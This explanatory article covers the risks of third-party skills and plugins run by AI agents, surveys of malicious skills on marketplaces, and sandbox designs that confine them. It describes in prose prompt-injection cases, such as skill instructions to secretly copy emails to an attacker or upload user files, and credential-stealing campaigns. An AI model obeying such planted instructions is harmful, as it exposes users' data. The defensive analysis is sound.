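# Running third-party scripts for AI agents: isolation, source review and update control

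## What third-party code does an AI agent run, and with whose permissions?

An AI agent is a program that uses a language model to choose actions, such as running a command or calling a tool, and carries them out for a user. The model only produces text, and the software around it, called the agent runtime, acts on that text. The runtime also loads add-ons and asks the user to approve actions before it executes them. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex are two runtimes that programmers use on their own machines.

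Much of what an AI agent's runtime executes comes from third parties rather than the user or the runtime's maker. Third parties write add-ons that equip an agent to handle a file format, query a database or follow a company's procedures, and users install them from public or private catalogues called marketplaces. Many add-ons contain code, and when an agent runs that code on the user's machine, the operating system by default gives it the same access as the user.

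*Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li, Wu and colleagues, 2026) traces current add-ons back to ChatGPT Plugins, which OpenAI offered in 2023 and 2024. Those plugins ran on their providers' servers, and OpenAI reviewed each one before listing it. They were hard to write, and few people used them. Their successors are easier to write and can do more, partly because they run where the user's files are.

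### The kinds of code

A skill is a folder that an agent loads when a task needs it. It contains an instruction file, SKILL.md, and optionally scripts and data. The scripts are typically in Python, Bash or JavaScript. Anthropic introduced the format in October 2025 and released it as an open standard that December. Several dozen products now support it, including Codex, Cursor, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI.

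A plugin is an installable package that can bundle skills, commands, tool servers and hooks, which are scripts triggered by events. The runtime starts hooks without the model deciding to, for instance when a session begins or after the agent edits a file. Anthropic's *Plugins reference* also describes monitors, which are shell commands that run in the background for a whole session. Monitors run outside any sandbox (an environment that limits which files, network addresses, processes and secrets a program can reach). A plugin's code can therefore run even if the agent never chooses to use the plugin.

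The tool servers follow the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data. An MCP server is a local or remote program that offers tools to an agent. A remote server runs on somebody else's computer. It receives what the agent sends and returns results, but its code cannot directly access the user's disk. A local server runs on the user's own machine, and MCP's security guidance warns that an attacker who gets code into one can execute any command with the privileges of the client, the part of the runtime that connects to the server. Anthropic cautions that, because plugins can also add servers, a project's own server list does not show every server that a session can load.

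Many programmers also run agents inside a code editor, alongside the editor's extensions. According to Visual Studio Code's *Extension runtime security*, an extension has the same permissions as the editor, so it can read and write files, make network requests and start other programs.

All of these rely on packages, the libraries that a script imports, which import further libraries. Add-ons can also depend on one another. Claude Code installs a plugin's declared dependencies together with the plugin, and in Visual Studio Code, trusting an extension's publisher means also trusting the publishers of the extensions it depends on. Someone who installs one add-on may therefore run code by a dozen authors after looking up only one of them.

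### One skill, from installation to execution

An invented example makes the sequence concrete. A small firm wants its agent to turn supplier invoices into a table, and an employee finds a skill for the job:

```
invoice-extraction/
├── SKILL.md
├── requirements.txt
└── scripts/
    └── extract.py
```

SKILL.md starts with a short header that gives the skill's name and describes its purpose, which is to extract the supplier, date and total from PDF invoices when someone asks for invoice data. The agent's instructions below the header are to run `extract.py` on a folder of invoices and report any file that failed. The script finds the supplier, invoice number, date and total in each PDF in `invoices/` and writes one row per invoice to `output/invoices.csv`. The dependency file, `requirements.txt`, lists only pdfplumber, with no version number. Pdfplumber is a real Python package for reading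 PDFs, and it depends on other packages.

The employee copies the folder into the runtime's skills directory and installs the library. The skill then loads in the sequence described in Anthropic's *Agent Skills*. At startup, the runtime puts the name and description of every installed skill in the system prompt, the text the model receives before any request. This uses about 100 tokens per skill. When the employee asks for last month's invoices as a table, the model compares the request with the descriptions and selects this skill. No fixed rule or register of verified skills determines the choice, so the author, who wrote the description, has a good deal of influence over when the agent picks the skill.

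Next the agent reads SKILL.md with a shell command, which puts the whole text into the model's context, the material it works from. Following those instructions, the agent runs `extract.py`. Only the script's output, perhaps "14 invoices read, 1 failed", enters the context, not its source code. Anthropic presents this as efficient, and it is, because even a long script uses no tokens. It also means the model acts on a result without having seen the code that produced it. An agent could read the script first, but the normal sequence doesn't include that step.

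Some runtimes ask the user to approve a command before running it. The user then sees a line that runs a Python file by name. That line looks the same whether the file only adds up invoice totals or also copies the user's passwords.

### Inherited permissions

When the runtime starts Python, the operating system creates a process under the user's account. It then checks what that account may do, regardless of who wrote the code. The new process normally also receives a copy of the runtime's environment variables, named values in which developers often keep passwords and access keys. Anthropic's *Discover and install prebuilt plugins through marketplaces* states that plugins "can execute arbitrary code on your machine with your user privileges".

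For the invoice skill, the distance between need and default is large:

| Resource | What the skill needs | What it gets by default on the user's machine |
|---|---|---|
| Files to read | The PDFs in `invoices/`, its own folder, Python and the installed packages | Every file the user can open, including SSH keys (which unlock remote servers) and browser data |
| Files to write | `output/invoices.csv` | Every file the user can change, including the agent's own settings |
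| Network | None while it runs; the package registry once, at installation | Every address the machine can reach |
| Secrets | None | Access keys in environment variables and credential files |
| Other programs | The Python interpreter | Any program the user can start |

Li and colleagues express the same gap in set notation. Let *A* be the set of all actions open to the agent, from file operations to network calls, and *D* the subset that a skill declares in its description and header. A user who installs the skill agrees to *D*, plus whatever else they happened to read, but the grant covers all of *A*. The difference, *A* ∖ *D*, is everything the skill can do but never declared. The grant also carries over into later sessions, and because it attaches to the skill's identity rather than a particular version, it remains in force when the skill's content changes.

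How far this applies depends on where the skill runs. Through the Claude API, the skill runs in a container with no network access and cannot install packages during execution. The invoice skill would work there only if Anthropic had already installed pdfplumber. In Claude Code, a skill has the same network access as any other program on the computer. Claude Code offers modes that restrict file and network access, but the skill format does not require them.

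The format also does not require an author to state what a skill needs. Agent Skills' *Specification* provides an optional field for environment requirements and an optional, experimental field, `allowed-tools`, for the tools a skill may use. Li and colleagues report that Claude Code applies `allowed-tools`, but that Anthropic's own Agent SDK, a toolkit for building agents, does not read it. Even where a runtime applies the field, the field controls only which tools the agent may call. Once the agent has permission to start `extract.py`, the field does not limit what the script opens or contacts.

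A user would want the guarantee that *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (Qu, Xu and colleagues, 2026) calls Tool Integrity. It requires the system to confine each skill, plugin or script to its declared interface and documented behaviour, so that the component cannot read unrelated files or contact unadvertised addresses. According to the paper, most defences for agents rely on tools being trustworthy. Those defences mainly target hostile text in emails and web pages, and were not built to stop a hostile `extract.py`.

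### Why the written instructions count as part of the program

SKILL.md determines which commands the agent runs, so it needs to be reviewed as carefully as `extract.py`, though a reviewer used to ordinary software may skim it as documentation. Suppose the author adds one sentence to SKILL.md telling the agent to send the finished table to a web address as a backup. The firm's invoice data would then leave the machine without any change to `extract.py`, because the agent has its own shell and network connection.

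The header deserves at least as much attention from reviewers as the body, because it enters the system prompt at startup for every installed skill, even one that the agent never activates. An MCP server's tool definitions need the same care, because the model reads them as text too. They include the names, descriptions and input schemas that specify what each tool does and accepts.

Text that the skill processes can also act as instructions. Database software solved a similar problem by sending commands and values through separate channels, so that a customer's name cannot be run as a command. Skills have no such separation. If `extract.py` prints a line that a supplier wrote on an invoice, the model receives that line alongside the skill's own directions.

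Unlike a Python interpreter, a language model may ignore or refuse an instruction, and Li and colleagues note that models react differently to identical attacks through skills. This makes written instructions a less reliable means of attack than a script. It also makes them harder to review, because nobody can work through every request to which they might apply. *A Systematic Survey of Agentic Skills* (Badhe, Shah and colleagues, 2026) accordingly classes skills as only partly verifiable before use, whereas a typed tool at least has a schema to check.

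A skill's effects can also outlast the task. Runtimes load standing instructions from files such as AGENTS.md and CLAUDE.md at the start of each session, so a skill that writes to those files changes how the agent behaves even in sessions where nobody uses the skill.

### Three sources of harm

In the clearest case, a malicious author builds an add-on to do damage, usually giving it a working function as cover. Qu and colleagues give the example of an image-generation skill with hidden code that reads the user's SSH key and sends it to a remote server. In the ClawHavoc campaign, attackers planted more than 1,000 malicious skills on the marketplace ClawHub.

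An attacker can also take over an honest author's project by stealing the author's credentials or claiming an abandoned account name, without having to win anyone's trust. The harmful version arrives through the original channel as a routine update, and it reaches people who checked the project months ago and correctly found nothing wrong. Kapner (2026), in *Securing Claude Code plug-ins*, concludes that installing a plugin means trusting the developer's entire release pipeline as well as the developer.

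An honest author can also make a careless change. A new release of `extract.py` might clear the output folder before writing to it and delete the firm's earlier tables. The Model Context Protocol's guidance lists bugs in legitimate servers, as well as attackers, as a possible cause of permanent data loss. Carelessness can also let an attacker in. Language models sometimes invent plausible names for packages that do not exist, and an author who writes a script with a model's help may publish it without checking the names. Li and colleagues cite findings by the firm Aikido Security that skills invoked such packages and that attackers later registered the names. The skill then installs the attacker's code, even though nobody has broken into the author's account.

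Anthropic's standard advice is to use only skills from trusted sources, meaning skills that users wrote themselves or obtained from Anthropic. This is a sound way to avoid malicious strangers, though it rules out nearly everything in a community marketplace. It does much less to prevent harm from account takeovers and mistakes, which can also affect trustworthy authors. Anthropic adds that even trustworthy skills can become compromised when their external dependencies change.

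### When each control acts

Source review takes place before the firm adopts a skill. Someone reads SKILL.md, the scripts and the dependency list, often with the help of automated scanners, and compares what the files do with what the skill needs. Isolation limits what the scripts can reach while they run. A sandbox, which can be anything from a set of operating-system rules to a separate virtual machine, lets `extract.py` reach the invoices and the output folder and blocks all other access, including any attempts the reviewer missed. Update control applies each time the skill changes. The firm switches off automatic updates and keeps running the version it reviewed until someone has examined and approved the new one.

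## How common are harmful skills, and what do they do?

Estimates of the share of public skills that are dangerous range from 0.16% to 26.1%. Much of the spread arises because some researchers counted only skills built to harm the user, while others counted any skill with a weakness. The estimates also depend heavily on the marketplace and the date, because one attacker can upload hundreds of skills in a few days.

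### The ClawHavoc campaign

OpenClaw is an AI assistant that people run on their own computers and connect to their email, calendars and chat accounts. In February 2026, the security company Koi audited all 2,857 skills on OpenClaw's marketplace, ClawHub. According to Koi's *ClawHavoc* (2026), 341 were malicious, and 335 of those appeared to come from a single campaign.

The 335 skills used nearly identical tactics. Each had professional-looking documentation for an ordinary tool, with a "Prerequisites" section where the attackers told the user to install something else first. On Windows, this was a trojan that recorded keystrokes, in a password-protected archive to keep antivirus scanners from seeing inside. On a Mac, the user had to paste a command that fetched Atomic Stealer, malware that criminals can buy for $500 to $1,000 a month. It copies browser data, keychain passwords, SSH keys,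 Telegram sessions, more than 60 kinds of cryptocurrency wallet and other data. The attackers hosted the malware on outside servers, so a reviewer who checked only the skill's own scripts could easily have missed it.

The attackers chose disguises that would appeal to many users or to wealthy ones. Koi counted 111 skills posing as cryptocurrency tools, 57 as YouTube utilities and 28 as automatic updaters, along with 29 whose names were misspellings or variants of "ClawHub".

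Six malicious skills were not part of the campaign. Three pushed a fake login tool, and one posed as a weather tool while sending the agent's stored credentials to an outside address. The other two, the hardest cases for a reviewer, contained what looked like working search code for a prediction market, with a backdoor around line 180 that opened when the user ran a search.

The Hacker News reported that, at the time, anyone with a GitHub account at least one week old could upload a skill to ClawHub. OpenClaw's creator, Peter Steinberger, responded by adding a reporting button, and the marketplace began hiding any skill that more than three users had reported.

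OpenClaw then added automatic checks through VirusTotal, Google's malware-scanning service. According to The Hacker News, ClawHub computes a digest of each skill, a short fingerprint of its bytes, and looks for a match in VirusTotal's database. If there is none, it uploads the skill to VirusTotal's Code Insight for analysis. ClawHub automatically approves skills rated benign, adds a warning to those rated suspicious, and blocks downloads of those rated malicious. It also re-scans every active skill daily. Its maintainers cautioned that cleverly hidden instructions might still get through.

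By 16 February, Koi had found 824 malicious skills among more than 10,700. The number had more than doubled, but the share had fallen from 12% to under 8% because the marketplace had grown even faster. *MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, 2026) cites a higher count of 1,184 from the security team Antiy CERT. The new checks did not catch every malicious skill. The scan described in *MalSkills* (2026) found 262 previously undisclosed ones in three registries that had security checks, including ClawHub.

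### Vulnerable, risky or malicious

A vulnerable skill has a flaw that somebody else could exploit, though its author meant no harm. The invoice skill is a mild example, since it would accept a bad release of pdfplumber. A risky skill has permissions that could allow serious damage. One that deploys software to a company's servers needs the keys to those servers, and it remains risky even if its code has no flaws. A malicious skill is built to do harm. An author can fix a vulnerability, and a firm can confine a risky skill and go on using it, but the firm has to remove a malicious skill.

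The often-cited figure that 26.1% of skills contain vulnerabilities comes from *Agent Skills in the Wild* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026), which analysed 31,132 skills collected from the catalogues skills.rest and skillsmp.com in December 2025. The paper uses "vulnerability" for malicious code, careless code and patterns that could merely enable harm, and its method could not reliably separate them. Pattern-matching rules and language-model classifiers selected candidates, and Claude 3.5 Sonnet helped decide which to count. The team did not run the skills, but when they tested the method on 200 skills that researchers had labelled by hand, 86.7% of its positive verdicts were correct. In a sample of 1,218 skills, the most common pattern was a dependency with no fixed version, which is also the fault in the invoice skill.

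They also put 5.2% of skills in a high-severity group whose patterns "strongly" suggest malicious intent. These patterns don't prove intent. For example, one of them is reading a credential file, which some legitimate tools have to do.

The figure is much lower when each vulnerability must be shown with a working attack. *Scan Before You Install* (2026) describes a scan of 2,197 skills in which three outside analysts checked the findings and the researchers built a demonstration attack for each of the 41 distinct vulnerabilities. These vulnerabilities accounted for 53 confirmed findings, of which 41 were low severity and one was high. At most 2.4% of the skills had a confirmed finding, though the scanner may have missed others.

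Risky permissions are much more common than either confirmed flaws or malice. *Beyond Maliciousness* (Pandey, Singh and colleagues, 2026) profiled 6,309 listings from skillsmp.com and ClawHub, excluding the most popular skills and the unused ones. Half showed evidence that they could run shell commands, 31% that they could send data over the network and 13% that they could reach credentials. The researchers judged about a quarter to carry serious exposure. Only one in twenty received a threat verdict, which means an automated score above a threshold. Human review of the flagged listings was unfinished, so that figure is not a rate of confirmed malice.

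### How the rate changes with the definition

In a scan by the security company Snyk, the share of skills counted as harmful depended on the definition used. Beurer-Kellner, Kudrinskii and colleagues (2026), in *Exploring the Threat Landscape of Agent Skills*, scanned 3,984 skills using language-model judges and fixed rules. They found that 13.4% had a critical issue, meaning malicious code, a suspicious download or prompt injection (text that steers an agent against its user's wishes), and 36.8% had at least one issue of lower severity. Manual review confirmed 76 skills, or 1.9%, as malicious.

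Snyk's 1.9% is much lower than Koi's 12%, although both concern mainly ClawHub in the same few weeks. Snyk's detector for suspicious downloads flagged 10.9% of ClawHub's skills, close to Koi's share. A plausible explanation is that Koi counted every copy in a campaign it had recognised, while Snyk's reviewers confirmed fewer of the skills their scanner had flagged.

The strictest of the large surveys, *Do Not Mention This to the User* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026), counted a skill as malicious only if researchers had seen it misbehave. The team collected 98,380 skills from skills.rest and skillsmp.com in January 2026, and used static rules and a language model to pick out 4,287 suspicious ones. They ran each of these in an isolated container with fake credentials as bait, recording its network traffic, file access and system calls. Two researchers then manually reviewed the 762 skills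 that showed suspicious activity, comparing what each one did with its documentation. They confirmed 157 as malicious, or 0.16% of the collection. Most of the other skills they reviewed were legitimate tools with security functions, such as credential managers and penetration-testing utilities.

That 0.16% is a lower bound, because the team ran only the skills that had matched a suspicious pattern and gave each run at most 60 seconds. Of the 413 unconfirmed candidates they examined, 93.2% contained triggers that had not activated in that time. Dormant triggers are not proof of malice, but if they all concealed attacks, the rate would be about 4%, not counting any harmful skills the initial rules missed.

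*HarmfulSkillBench*, by Jiang, Zhang and colleagues, covers a collection of almost the same size but focuses on a different victim. It calls a skill harmful if its intended use breaks the usage policies of AI companies, so the person installing it is the attacker and the victim is somebody else, such as the target of a scam. The definition also includes financial or medical advice given without human review or a notice that AI produced it. A language model scored 98,440 skills from their names, descriptions and section headings, without running them. It classed 4.93% as harmful, with a precision of 0.74 on a hand-labelled sample, so roughly one in four positive verdicts was wrong. The percentage is of little use for judging the risk that a skill will steal its user's passwords.

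| Survey | Skills | What it counted | How the researchers confirmed it | Share |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Liu and colleagues, *Agent Skills in the Wild* | 31,132 | Malicious, careless or dangerous patterns | Rules and language models; no skills run | 26.1% |
| Beurer-Kellner and colleagues | 3,984 | Critical issues | Automated scan | 13.4% |
| Koi | 2,857 | Malicious skills | A researcher validated every finding | 11.9% |
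| Pandey and colleagues | 6,309 | Threat verdicts | Automated scoring; human review unfinished | About 5% |
| Jiang and colleagues | 98,440 | Uses that break AI policies | Language-model scoring; no skills run | 4.93% |
| *Scan Before You Install* | 2,197 | Exploitable flaws | Three analysts and demonstration attacks | At most 2.4% |
| Beurer-Kellner and colleagues | 3,984 | Malicious skills | Manual review | 1.9% |
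| *MalSkills* | 150,108 | Malicious skills | Manual review of 620 flagged skills | 0.27% |
| Liu and colleagues, *Do Not Mention This to the User* | 98,380 | Malicious skills | Sandbox runs, then two reviewers | 0.16% |

Even the figures for malicious skills alone differ by a factor of more than 70. Koi examined a young marketplace during a mass upload, whereas skills.rest and skillsmp.com mostly index public GitHub repositories. One actor was responsible for 85 of the 157 skills in the 0.16% figure. These rates depend heavily on whether a campaign is under way and are a poor guide to the odds that a particular skill is malicious.

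### What malicious skills do

Most confirmed malicious skills try to get outside code onto the machine, steal credentials, or both. Among the 157 that Liu and colleagues confirmed, 75.2% fetched and ran remote code or injected commands, 68.2% accessed credentials, and 57.3% used techniques for sending data out. The shares overlap because a typical skill combined several techniques. The actor behind the 85 skills specialized in brand impersonation, posing as 85 different companies and assuring users that their credentials were "never transmitted".

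Other collections show a similar mix. In *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026), 34 of the 82 hidden malicious skills (41%) were malicious installers, and credential theft was the other dominant goal. Backdoors are harder to count separately, because an installer can deliver one along with a password stealer. A skill that downloads its code or instructions at run time also gives whoever controls the download a way back in. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues found such remote dependencies in 21% of their confirmed malicious skills.

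A skill's instructions can cause harm without any malicious script. One email skill in the 157 told the agent to add the attacker as a hidden recipient of every message and not to mention it to the user. Sixteen skills, about 10%, tried to override the agent's instructions without fetching remote code. In the same survey, 84.2% of the individual problems were in SKILL.md, but these include download commands written into the instructions as well as purely verbal manipulation. Harmful instructions and malicious code often appear together. All 76 malicious skills in Snyk's set contained malicious code, and 91% also used prompt injection.

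The change that makes a skill harmful can be very small. One attacker copied a legitimate presentation skill almost word for word and added three lines that had the agent run a "backup" script, which uploaded the user's files. In 73.2% of the 157 harmful skills, the researchers found a function that a user could not have inferred from the documentation, so comparing a skill's stated purpose with its actual behaviour is one of the more useful checks.

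### How MalSkillBench was built

Malicious skills caught in public marketplaces test detection tools on a narrow range of attacks. Guo and colleagues collected 703 malicious skills from ClawHub by starting with published incident reports, following the same accounts to other skills and recovering deleted versions from repository histories. Malware delivery was the main behaviour in 86.6%, usually through a false prerequisite, and two accounts had published 81%. Credential theft was the main behaviour in 33 skills and data exfiltration in 18. Only 12 (1.7%) targeted the agent's own goals, identity or instructions. Because the search began with known incidents, these shares reflect a few large campaigns more than malicious skills in general.

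To cover attacks missing from the campaigns, the researchers generated more examples. They defined 108 combinations of where an attack sits, what it does and how its author hides it. A language model without the usual refusals wrote candidates by adapting known attacks to fit inside legitimate-looking skills. A coding agent loaded each candidate in an isolated container and received a request matching the skill's advertised purpose, while monitoring software recorded what happened. A candidate passed if the expected behaviour appeared in the record or if a second model judged with enough confidence that it had occurred. Candidates that failed were rewritten up to three times.

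Of 3,757 candidates, 3,214 passed. The pass rate was 94.5% for attacks in code and 75.8% for attacks in written instructions, which also passed if the agent noticed the manipulation and refused. Passing therefore did not always mean that the attack had worked. Two reviewers checked 300 of the accepted skills and agreed with every label. *MalSkillBench* contains 3,944 malicious skills, including 27 from existing tools' test suites, and 4,000 popular ClawHub skills presumed harmless. Its builders chose that ratio, so it cannot show how common malicious skills are.

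### Why installs are not victims

The download counts on ClawHub do not show how many people a malicious skill has harmed. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that these figures can be inflated, which also makes popularity a poor sign of safety. Researchers also add to the totals when they download a whole marketplace for an audit. Even installing a malicious skill may not cause harm. In ClawHavoc, someone also had to install the false prerequisite. Other attacks depend on the agent using the skill, which it may never do.

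The count can also be too low. Skillsmp.com shows GitHub stars instead of downloads, and no marketplace records an installation when a user copies a skill's folder from a colleague. One installation on a work computer may expose a whole team's passwords. The surveys examined only the skills, so counting victims would require evidence from the machines that ran them or from the servers that received the stolen data.

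## How does a sandbox confine a script?

A malicious script has to read files, start programs or open connections to steal a password or install a backdoor. It can do these things only through the kernel, the core of the operating system, which controls the disk, network and memory. Each request to the kernel is called a system call. For example, when `extract.py` opens an invoice, Python makes a system call containing the file's path, and the kernel returns either access to the file or an error.

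By default, the kernel allows or refuses a program's system calls based only on the user's account. Some sandboxes add checks that apply to one program, and others give the program a separate kernel. WebAssembly, described below, prevents the program from making system calls at all.

### What a sandbox controls

A file policy lists the folders a program may read and the folders it may change. A network policy sets what the program may connect to, if anything. Anthropic's sandbox for Claude Code gives commands no direct route to the network, so their traffic has to pass through a proxy, a relay outside the sandbox that checks the name of each requested server against a list of allowed servers. Most database drivers ignore proxy settings, so they fail to connect even when their server is on the list.

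The limits also have to cover every process the script starts, or `extract.py` could escape them by launching a second program. Many sandboxes block system calls that ordinary programs rarely need, because a hostile script could exploit a bug in the kernel code that handles any call it can make.

File rules cannot protect an access key that the script inherits in an environment variable, so secrets need their own rules. Claude Code can remove chosen variables before a command starts. It can also mask them by giving the command a placeholder, which the proxy replaces with the real key in requests to approved servers. The script can then use the key without ever holding it. Claude Code has no built-in list of credentials, so it protects only those the user names.

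Limits on memory, processor time and the number of processes stop a runaway script from freezing the machine. On Linux, a kernel feature called cgroups can enforce them. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) describes a sandbox that counts the memory a program requests instead of using cgroups. Wang and Zheng consider this good enough for buggy code, but recommend cgroups against a program that deliberately tries to exhaust the kernel's memory.

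### Why file and network limits need each other

If a script can read an SSH key and open any connection, it can send the key away. Blocking network access prevents this only if the sandbox also limits which files the script can write. For example, a script without network access might still be able to write to `.bashrc`, a file of commands that the user's shell runs whenever a terminal opens. It could then add a command that sends the key, which would run outside the sandbox with full network access the next time the user opens a terminal.

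Claude Code blocks writes to shell startup files, its own settings and its skills folder, even inside an otherwise writable working folder. Codex keeps the `.git`, `.codex` and `.agents` folders read-only for sandboxed commands.

The dependence also matters when a user loosens a policy. Letting commands read the whole disk may be tolerable while the sandbox blocks network access, but a script could send anything on that disk to any server the user later approves.

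### Rules on a single process

The lightest sandboxes run the script as an ordinary process on the user's machine, and the existing kernel applies extra rules to it. On macOS, the built-in Seatbelt framework does this, and both Claude Code and Codex use it.

On Linux, developers combine several tools to confine a script. One of them, Bubblewrap, starts a program in new namespaces. A namespace gives a process its own version of something that programs normally share, such as the folder tree or the list of network connections. Bubblewrap can assemble a folder tree in which some real folders are read-only, some are writable and the rest are missing. It can also give the program a network namespace with no connection to the outside.

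Landlock attaches a list of permitted paths and network ports to the process without changing the folder tree. The process cannot remove these restrictions, and any program it starts inherits them. Seccomp filters system calls by type. A seccomp filter cannot read a file path, because the call contains only the path's memory address, but it can pause a call and pass it to a supervising program.

Sandlock, for example, first creates a child process, which applies the Landlock rules to itself and installs the seccomp filter. The child waits until the supervisor is ready, then loads the untrusted script. From then on, the kernel handles most system calls itself and sends the supervisor only decisions that depend on details, such as which server a connection is for.

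Sandlock's supervisor copies the destination address once, checks the copy and uses that same copy to open the connection itself. If it checked the address and then let the script's original call continue, another thread of the script could change the address in memory between the check and the connection.

Wang and Zheng, who developed Sandlock, ran ten checks on it, including reads outside the permitted folders and connections to unlisted servers, and all ten gave the results the policy required. The checks tested whether Sandlock operated correctly and did not include attempts by attackers to break it. On a laptop-class processor, Sandlock added about 5 ms to the start of a command, and Docker took 44 times as long as Sandlock in total. A database ran at full speed under Sandlock and at about 76% of full speed under Docker.

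In all these tools, the script runs on the host's kernel, which also enforces the sandbox's rules, so a script that exploits a kernel bug can get past them. Wang and Zheng say Sandlock is not meant to stop such exploits, and they recommend a small virtual machine where hostile programs from different customers share a computer.

### Containers

A container is one or more processes with their own folder tree, process list and network. Namespaces, which bubblewrap also uses, keep these separate from the host's, and cgroups cap the container's memory and processor time. The folder tree comes from an image, a package holding the program and the libraries it needs. Docker is the best-known container software. A container shares the host's kernel, so a kernel bug is as dangerous here as it is with process rules.

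van Rijn and Rellermeyer (2021), in *A Fresh Look at the Architecture and Performance of Contemporary Isolation Platforms*, timed 300 starts of each system they tested. A Docker container took around 100 ms when they started it directly, and about 250 ms more through Docker's background service, which is how most people use it. Disk access was close to normal speed, and network throughput fell by about 10%.

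### A kernel in user space

Google's gVisor puts a substitute kernel, called the Sentry, between the script and the real kernel. The Sentry runs as an ordinary program without special privileges. When the script tries to open a file, gVisor intercepts the system call and sends it to the Sentry. The Sentry is not allowed to open files either, so it passes the request to a separate process, the Gofer, which opens the file. For its other work, the Sentry uses a small set of system calls to the real kernel, and a seccomp filter blocks the rest. An attacker who took over the Sentry would still be confined by that filter and a set of namespaces.

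Handling system calls in the Sentry slows scripts down. In van Rijn and Rellermeyer's tests, which are five years old, gVisor started in about 190 ms, but its disk throughput was at best half that of most other systems, and its slowest network responses took three to four times as long. Some build tools that depend on exact kernel behaviour also run into problems, because the Sentry reimplements Linux instead of running it.

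In the same tests, Van Rijn and Rellermeyer found that gVisor and a similar product, Kata Containers, made more system calls to the host than ordinary containers did, which gave them a larger attack surface by the metric used. This counts against gVisor's usual selling point, and they concluded that any security advantage must come from having several layers. That seems right, though the metric is a poor measure of how freely a hostile script can choose those calls. A script in an ordinary container makes them directly, but in gVisor it has to go through the Sentry.

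### Small virtual machines

A virtual machine has its own kernel, running on simulated hardware. When a script in the machine makes a system call, this guest kernel handles it, and the host handles only traffic to a virtual disk or network card. To escape to the host, the script normally has to compromise the guest kernel and then exploit a flaw in the hypervisor, the software that runs the virtual machine.

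Firecracker, which Amazon developed for its cloud services, keeps that second target small. It simulates seven devices, compared with more than 40 in QEMU, a general-purpose alternative. Virtual machines this minimal are called microVMs.

Reported start-up times for Firecracker differ by a factor of ten. Jain (2020), in *Study of Firecracker MicroVM*, gives the project's own figures: 125 ms to reach the application, less than 5 MB of extra memory, and up to 150 new machines a second. Van Rijn and Rellermeyer measured about 350 ms from process creation to exit. They criticized the developers' method for leaving out the time before the kernel launched and after it signaled that it was running. *Benchmarking, Analysis, and Optimization of Serverless Function Snapshots* recorded 700 to 1,300 ms with the software that cloud companies put around Firecracker, which also has to mount a container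 image.

### WebAssembly

WebAssembly is a portable format for compiled programs, originally designed for web browsers. A WebAssembly program works in its own block of memory and has no instruction for making a system call. It can only call functions provided by the runtime that executes it. To let the program use files, the runtime passes it a handle to a particular folder, and the program can open only the files and subfolders inside it.

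A capability is a permission that a program holds as an object, like this handle. A WebAssembly version of the invoice script would receive a read-only handle to `invoices/`, a writable one to `output/`, and no networking functions. Nobody would have to write a rule against reading SSH keys, because the script would have no way to refer to them.

The drawback is that someone has to compile the program and all its libraries to WebAssembly. Python itself runs as WebAssembly, but pdfplumber depends on Pillow, an imaging library partly written in C that needs a special build. A bug in the WebAssembly runtime would also give the script whatever permissions the runtime's own process has. *Mewz* (2024) adds a second barrier by running WebAssembly on a unikernel, a minimal operating system built for one application.

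### How the designs compare

| Design | What enforces the boundary | Start-up time | Compatibility | What a flaw exposes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Process rules (Seatbelt, bubblewrap, Landlock, seccomp) | The host's kernel | About 5 ms for Sandlock | Ordinary programs, once the policy covers the files they need | A kernel bug exposes the whole computer |
| Container (Docker) | The host's kernel | About 100 ms, or 350 ms through Docker's service | Most Linux programs, packed in an image | A kernel bug exposes the whole computer |
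| Kernel in user space (gVisor) | The Sentry, backed by the host's kernel | About 190 ms | Most Linux programs, with slower disk and network access | A bug in the Sentry exposes a process with few permissions |
| Small virtual machine (Firecracker) | A guest kernel and a hypervisor | 125 to 1,300 ms, depending on what the timing includes | Linux programs, on hardware that supports virtualization | A guest kernel bug exposes the virtual machine; a hypervisor bug can expose the computer |
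| WebAssembly | The WebAssembly runtime | Not measured in these tests | Only programs compiled for it | A bug in the runtime exposes its process and that process's permissions |

The times come from different machines and years, so small differences mean little. They also leave out downloading and unpacking packages, which can be the slowest part for an agent. *Readie* (Sivaraman, Li and colleagues, 2026) timed a container that needed three large Python packages and had no stored copy of its image. It took 17.4 seconds to be ready, including 15 seconds to download and unpack the layer with the packages. Restoring a snapshot (a saved copy of a running sandbox's memory) with one such package already loaded took 0.29 to 0.42 seconds. A firm with a slow sandbox may therefore save more time by preparing packages in advance than by choosing a weaker boundary.

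The ranking by strength is less certain than the table may suggest. *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026) accepts that a microVM isolates better than a container, but argues that how a microVM compares with Seatbelt depends on the kind of attack one expects.

For someone installing skills, the sandbox's policy usually matters more than the type of boundary. The credential stealers on ClawHub needed readable passwords and an open connection, not a kernel bug. Process rules can deny both, but a virtual machine with the user's home folder mounted and unrestricted internet access would still let a script read the passwords and send them out.

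### A policy for the invoice skill

In Codex, a user can turn most of the invoice skill's short list of needs into a permission profile, using the format in OpenAI's *Permissions*:

```toml
default_permissions = "invoices"

[permissions.invoices.filesystem]
":minimal" = "read"
"~/skills/invoice-extraction" = "read"
"~/venvs/invoices" = "read"

[permissions.invoices.filesystem.":workspace_roots"]
"invoices" = "read"
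"output" = "write"

[permissions.invoices.network]
enabled = false
```

The `:minimal` entry covers system files that common tools need to run. The two paths below it are the skill's folder and the folder where the employee installed pdfplumber. The workspace is the firm's project folder. The profile opens only two subfolders in it and blocks access to everything else.

Permission profiles have no setting for environment variables, so the firm should also start Codex from a session that holds no access keys. The profiles also do not limit memory or processor time, so the firm would need a container or a virtual machine to limit those.

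Suppose a new release of `extract.py` tries to read `~/.ssh/id_ed25519`, a common location for a private key. On Linux, Codex uses bubblewrap, which restricts the view of the disk before Python starts. When Python makes the system call to open the key, the kernel finds no readable file at that path in the sandbox and returns an error, even if the employee's account may read the key. Under Landlock, the file would still appear in its folder, but the kernel would block Python from opening it because no rule covers that path. In a virtual machine, the file would not exist unless somebody had copied or mounted it there.

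Next the script tries to contact a server. It first has to look up the server's address, and the lookup fails because the sandbox has no route to the network. If the script already has a numeric address, the connection fails for the same reason. Starting another program, such as curl, doesn't help because the new process inherits the same limits.

Whether the employee notices the attempt depends on how the script handles errors. If it crashes, the agent receives a message naming the SSH key, which is a strong warning because a tool that reads invoices has no reason to open one. A more careful attacker would write the script to ignore the error and produce the table as usual. The sandbox would still protect the key, but nobody would know the skill was malicious.

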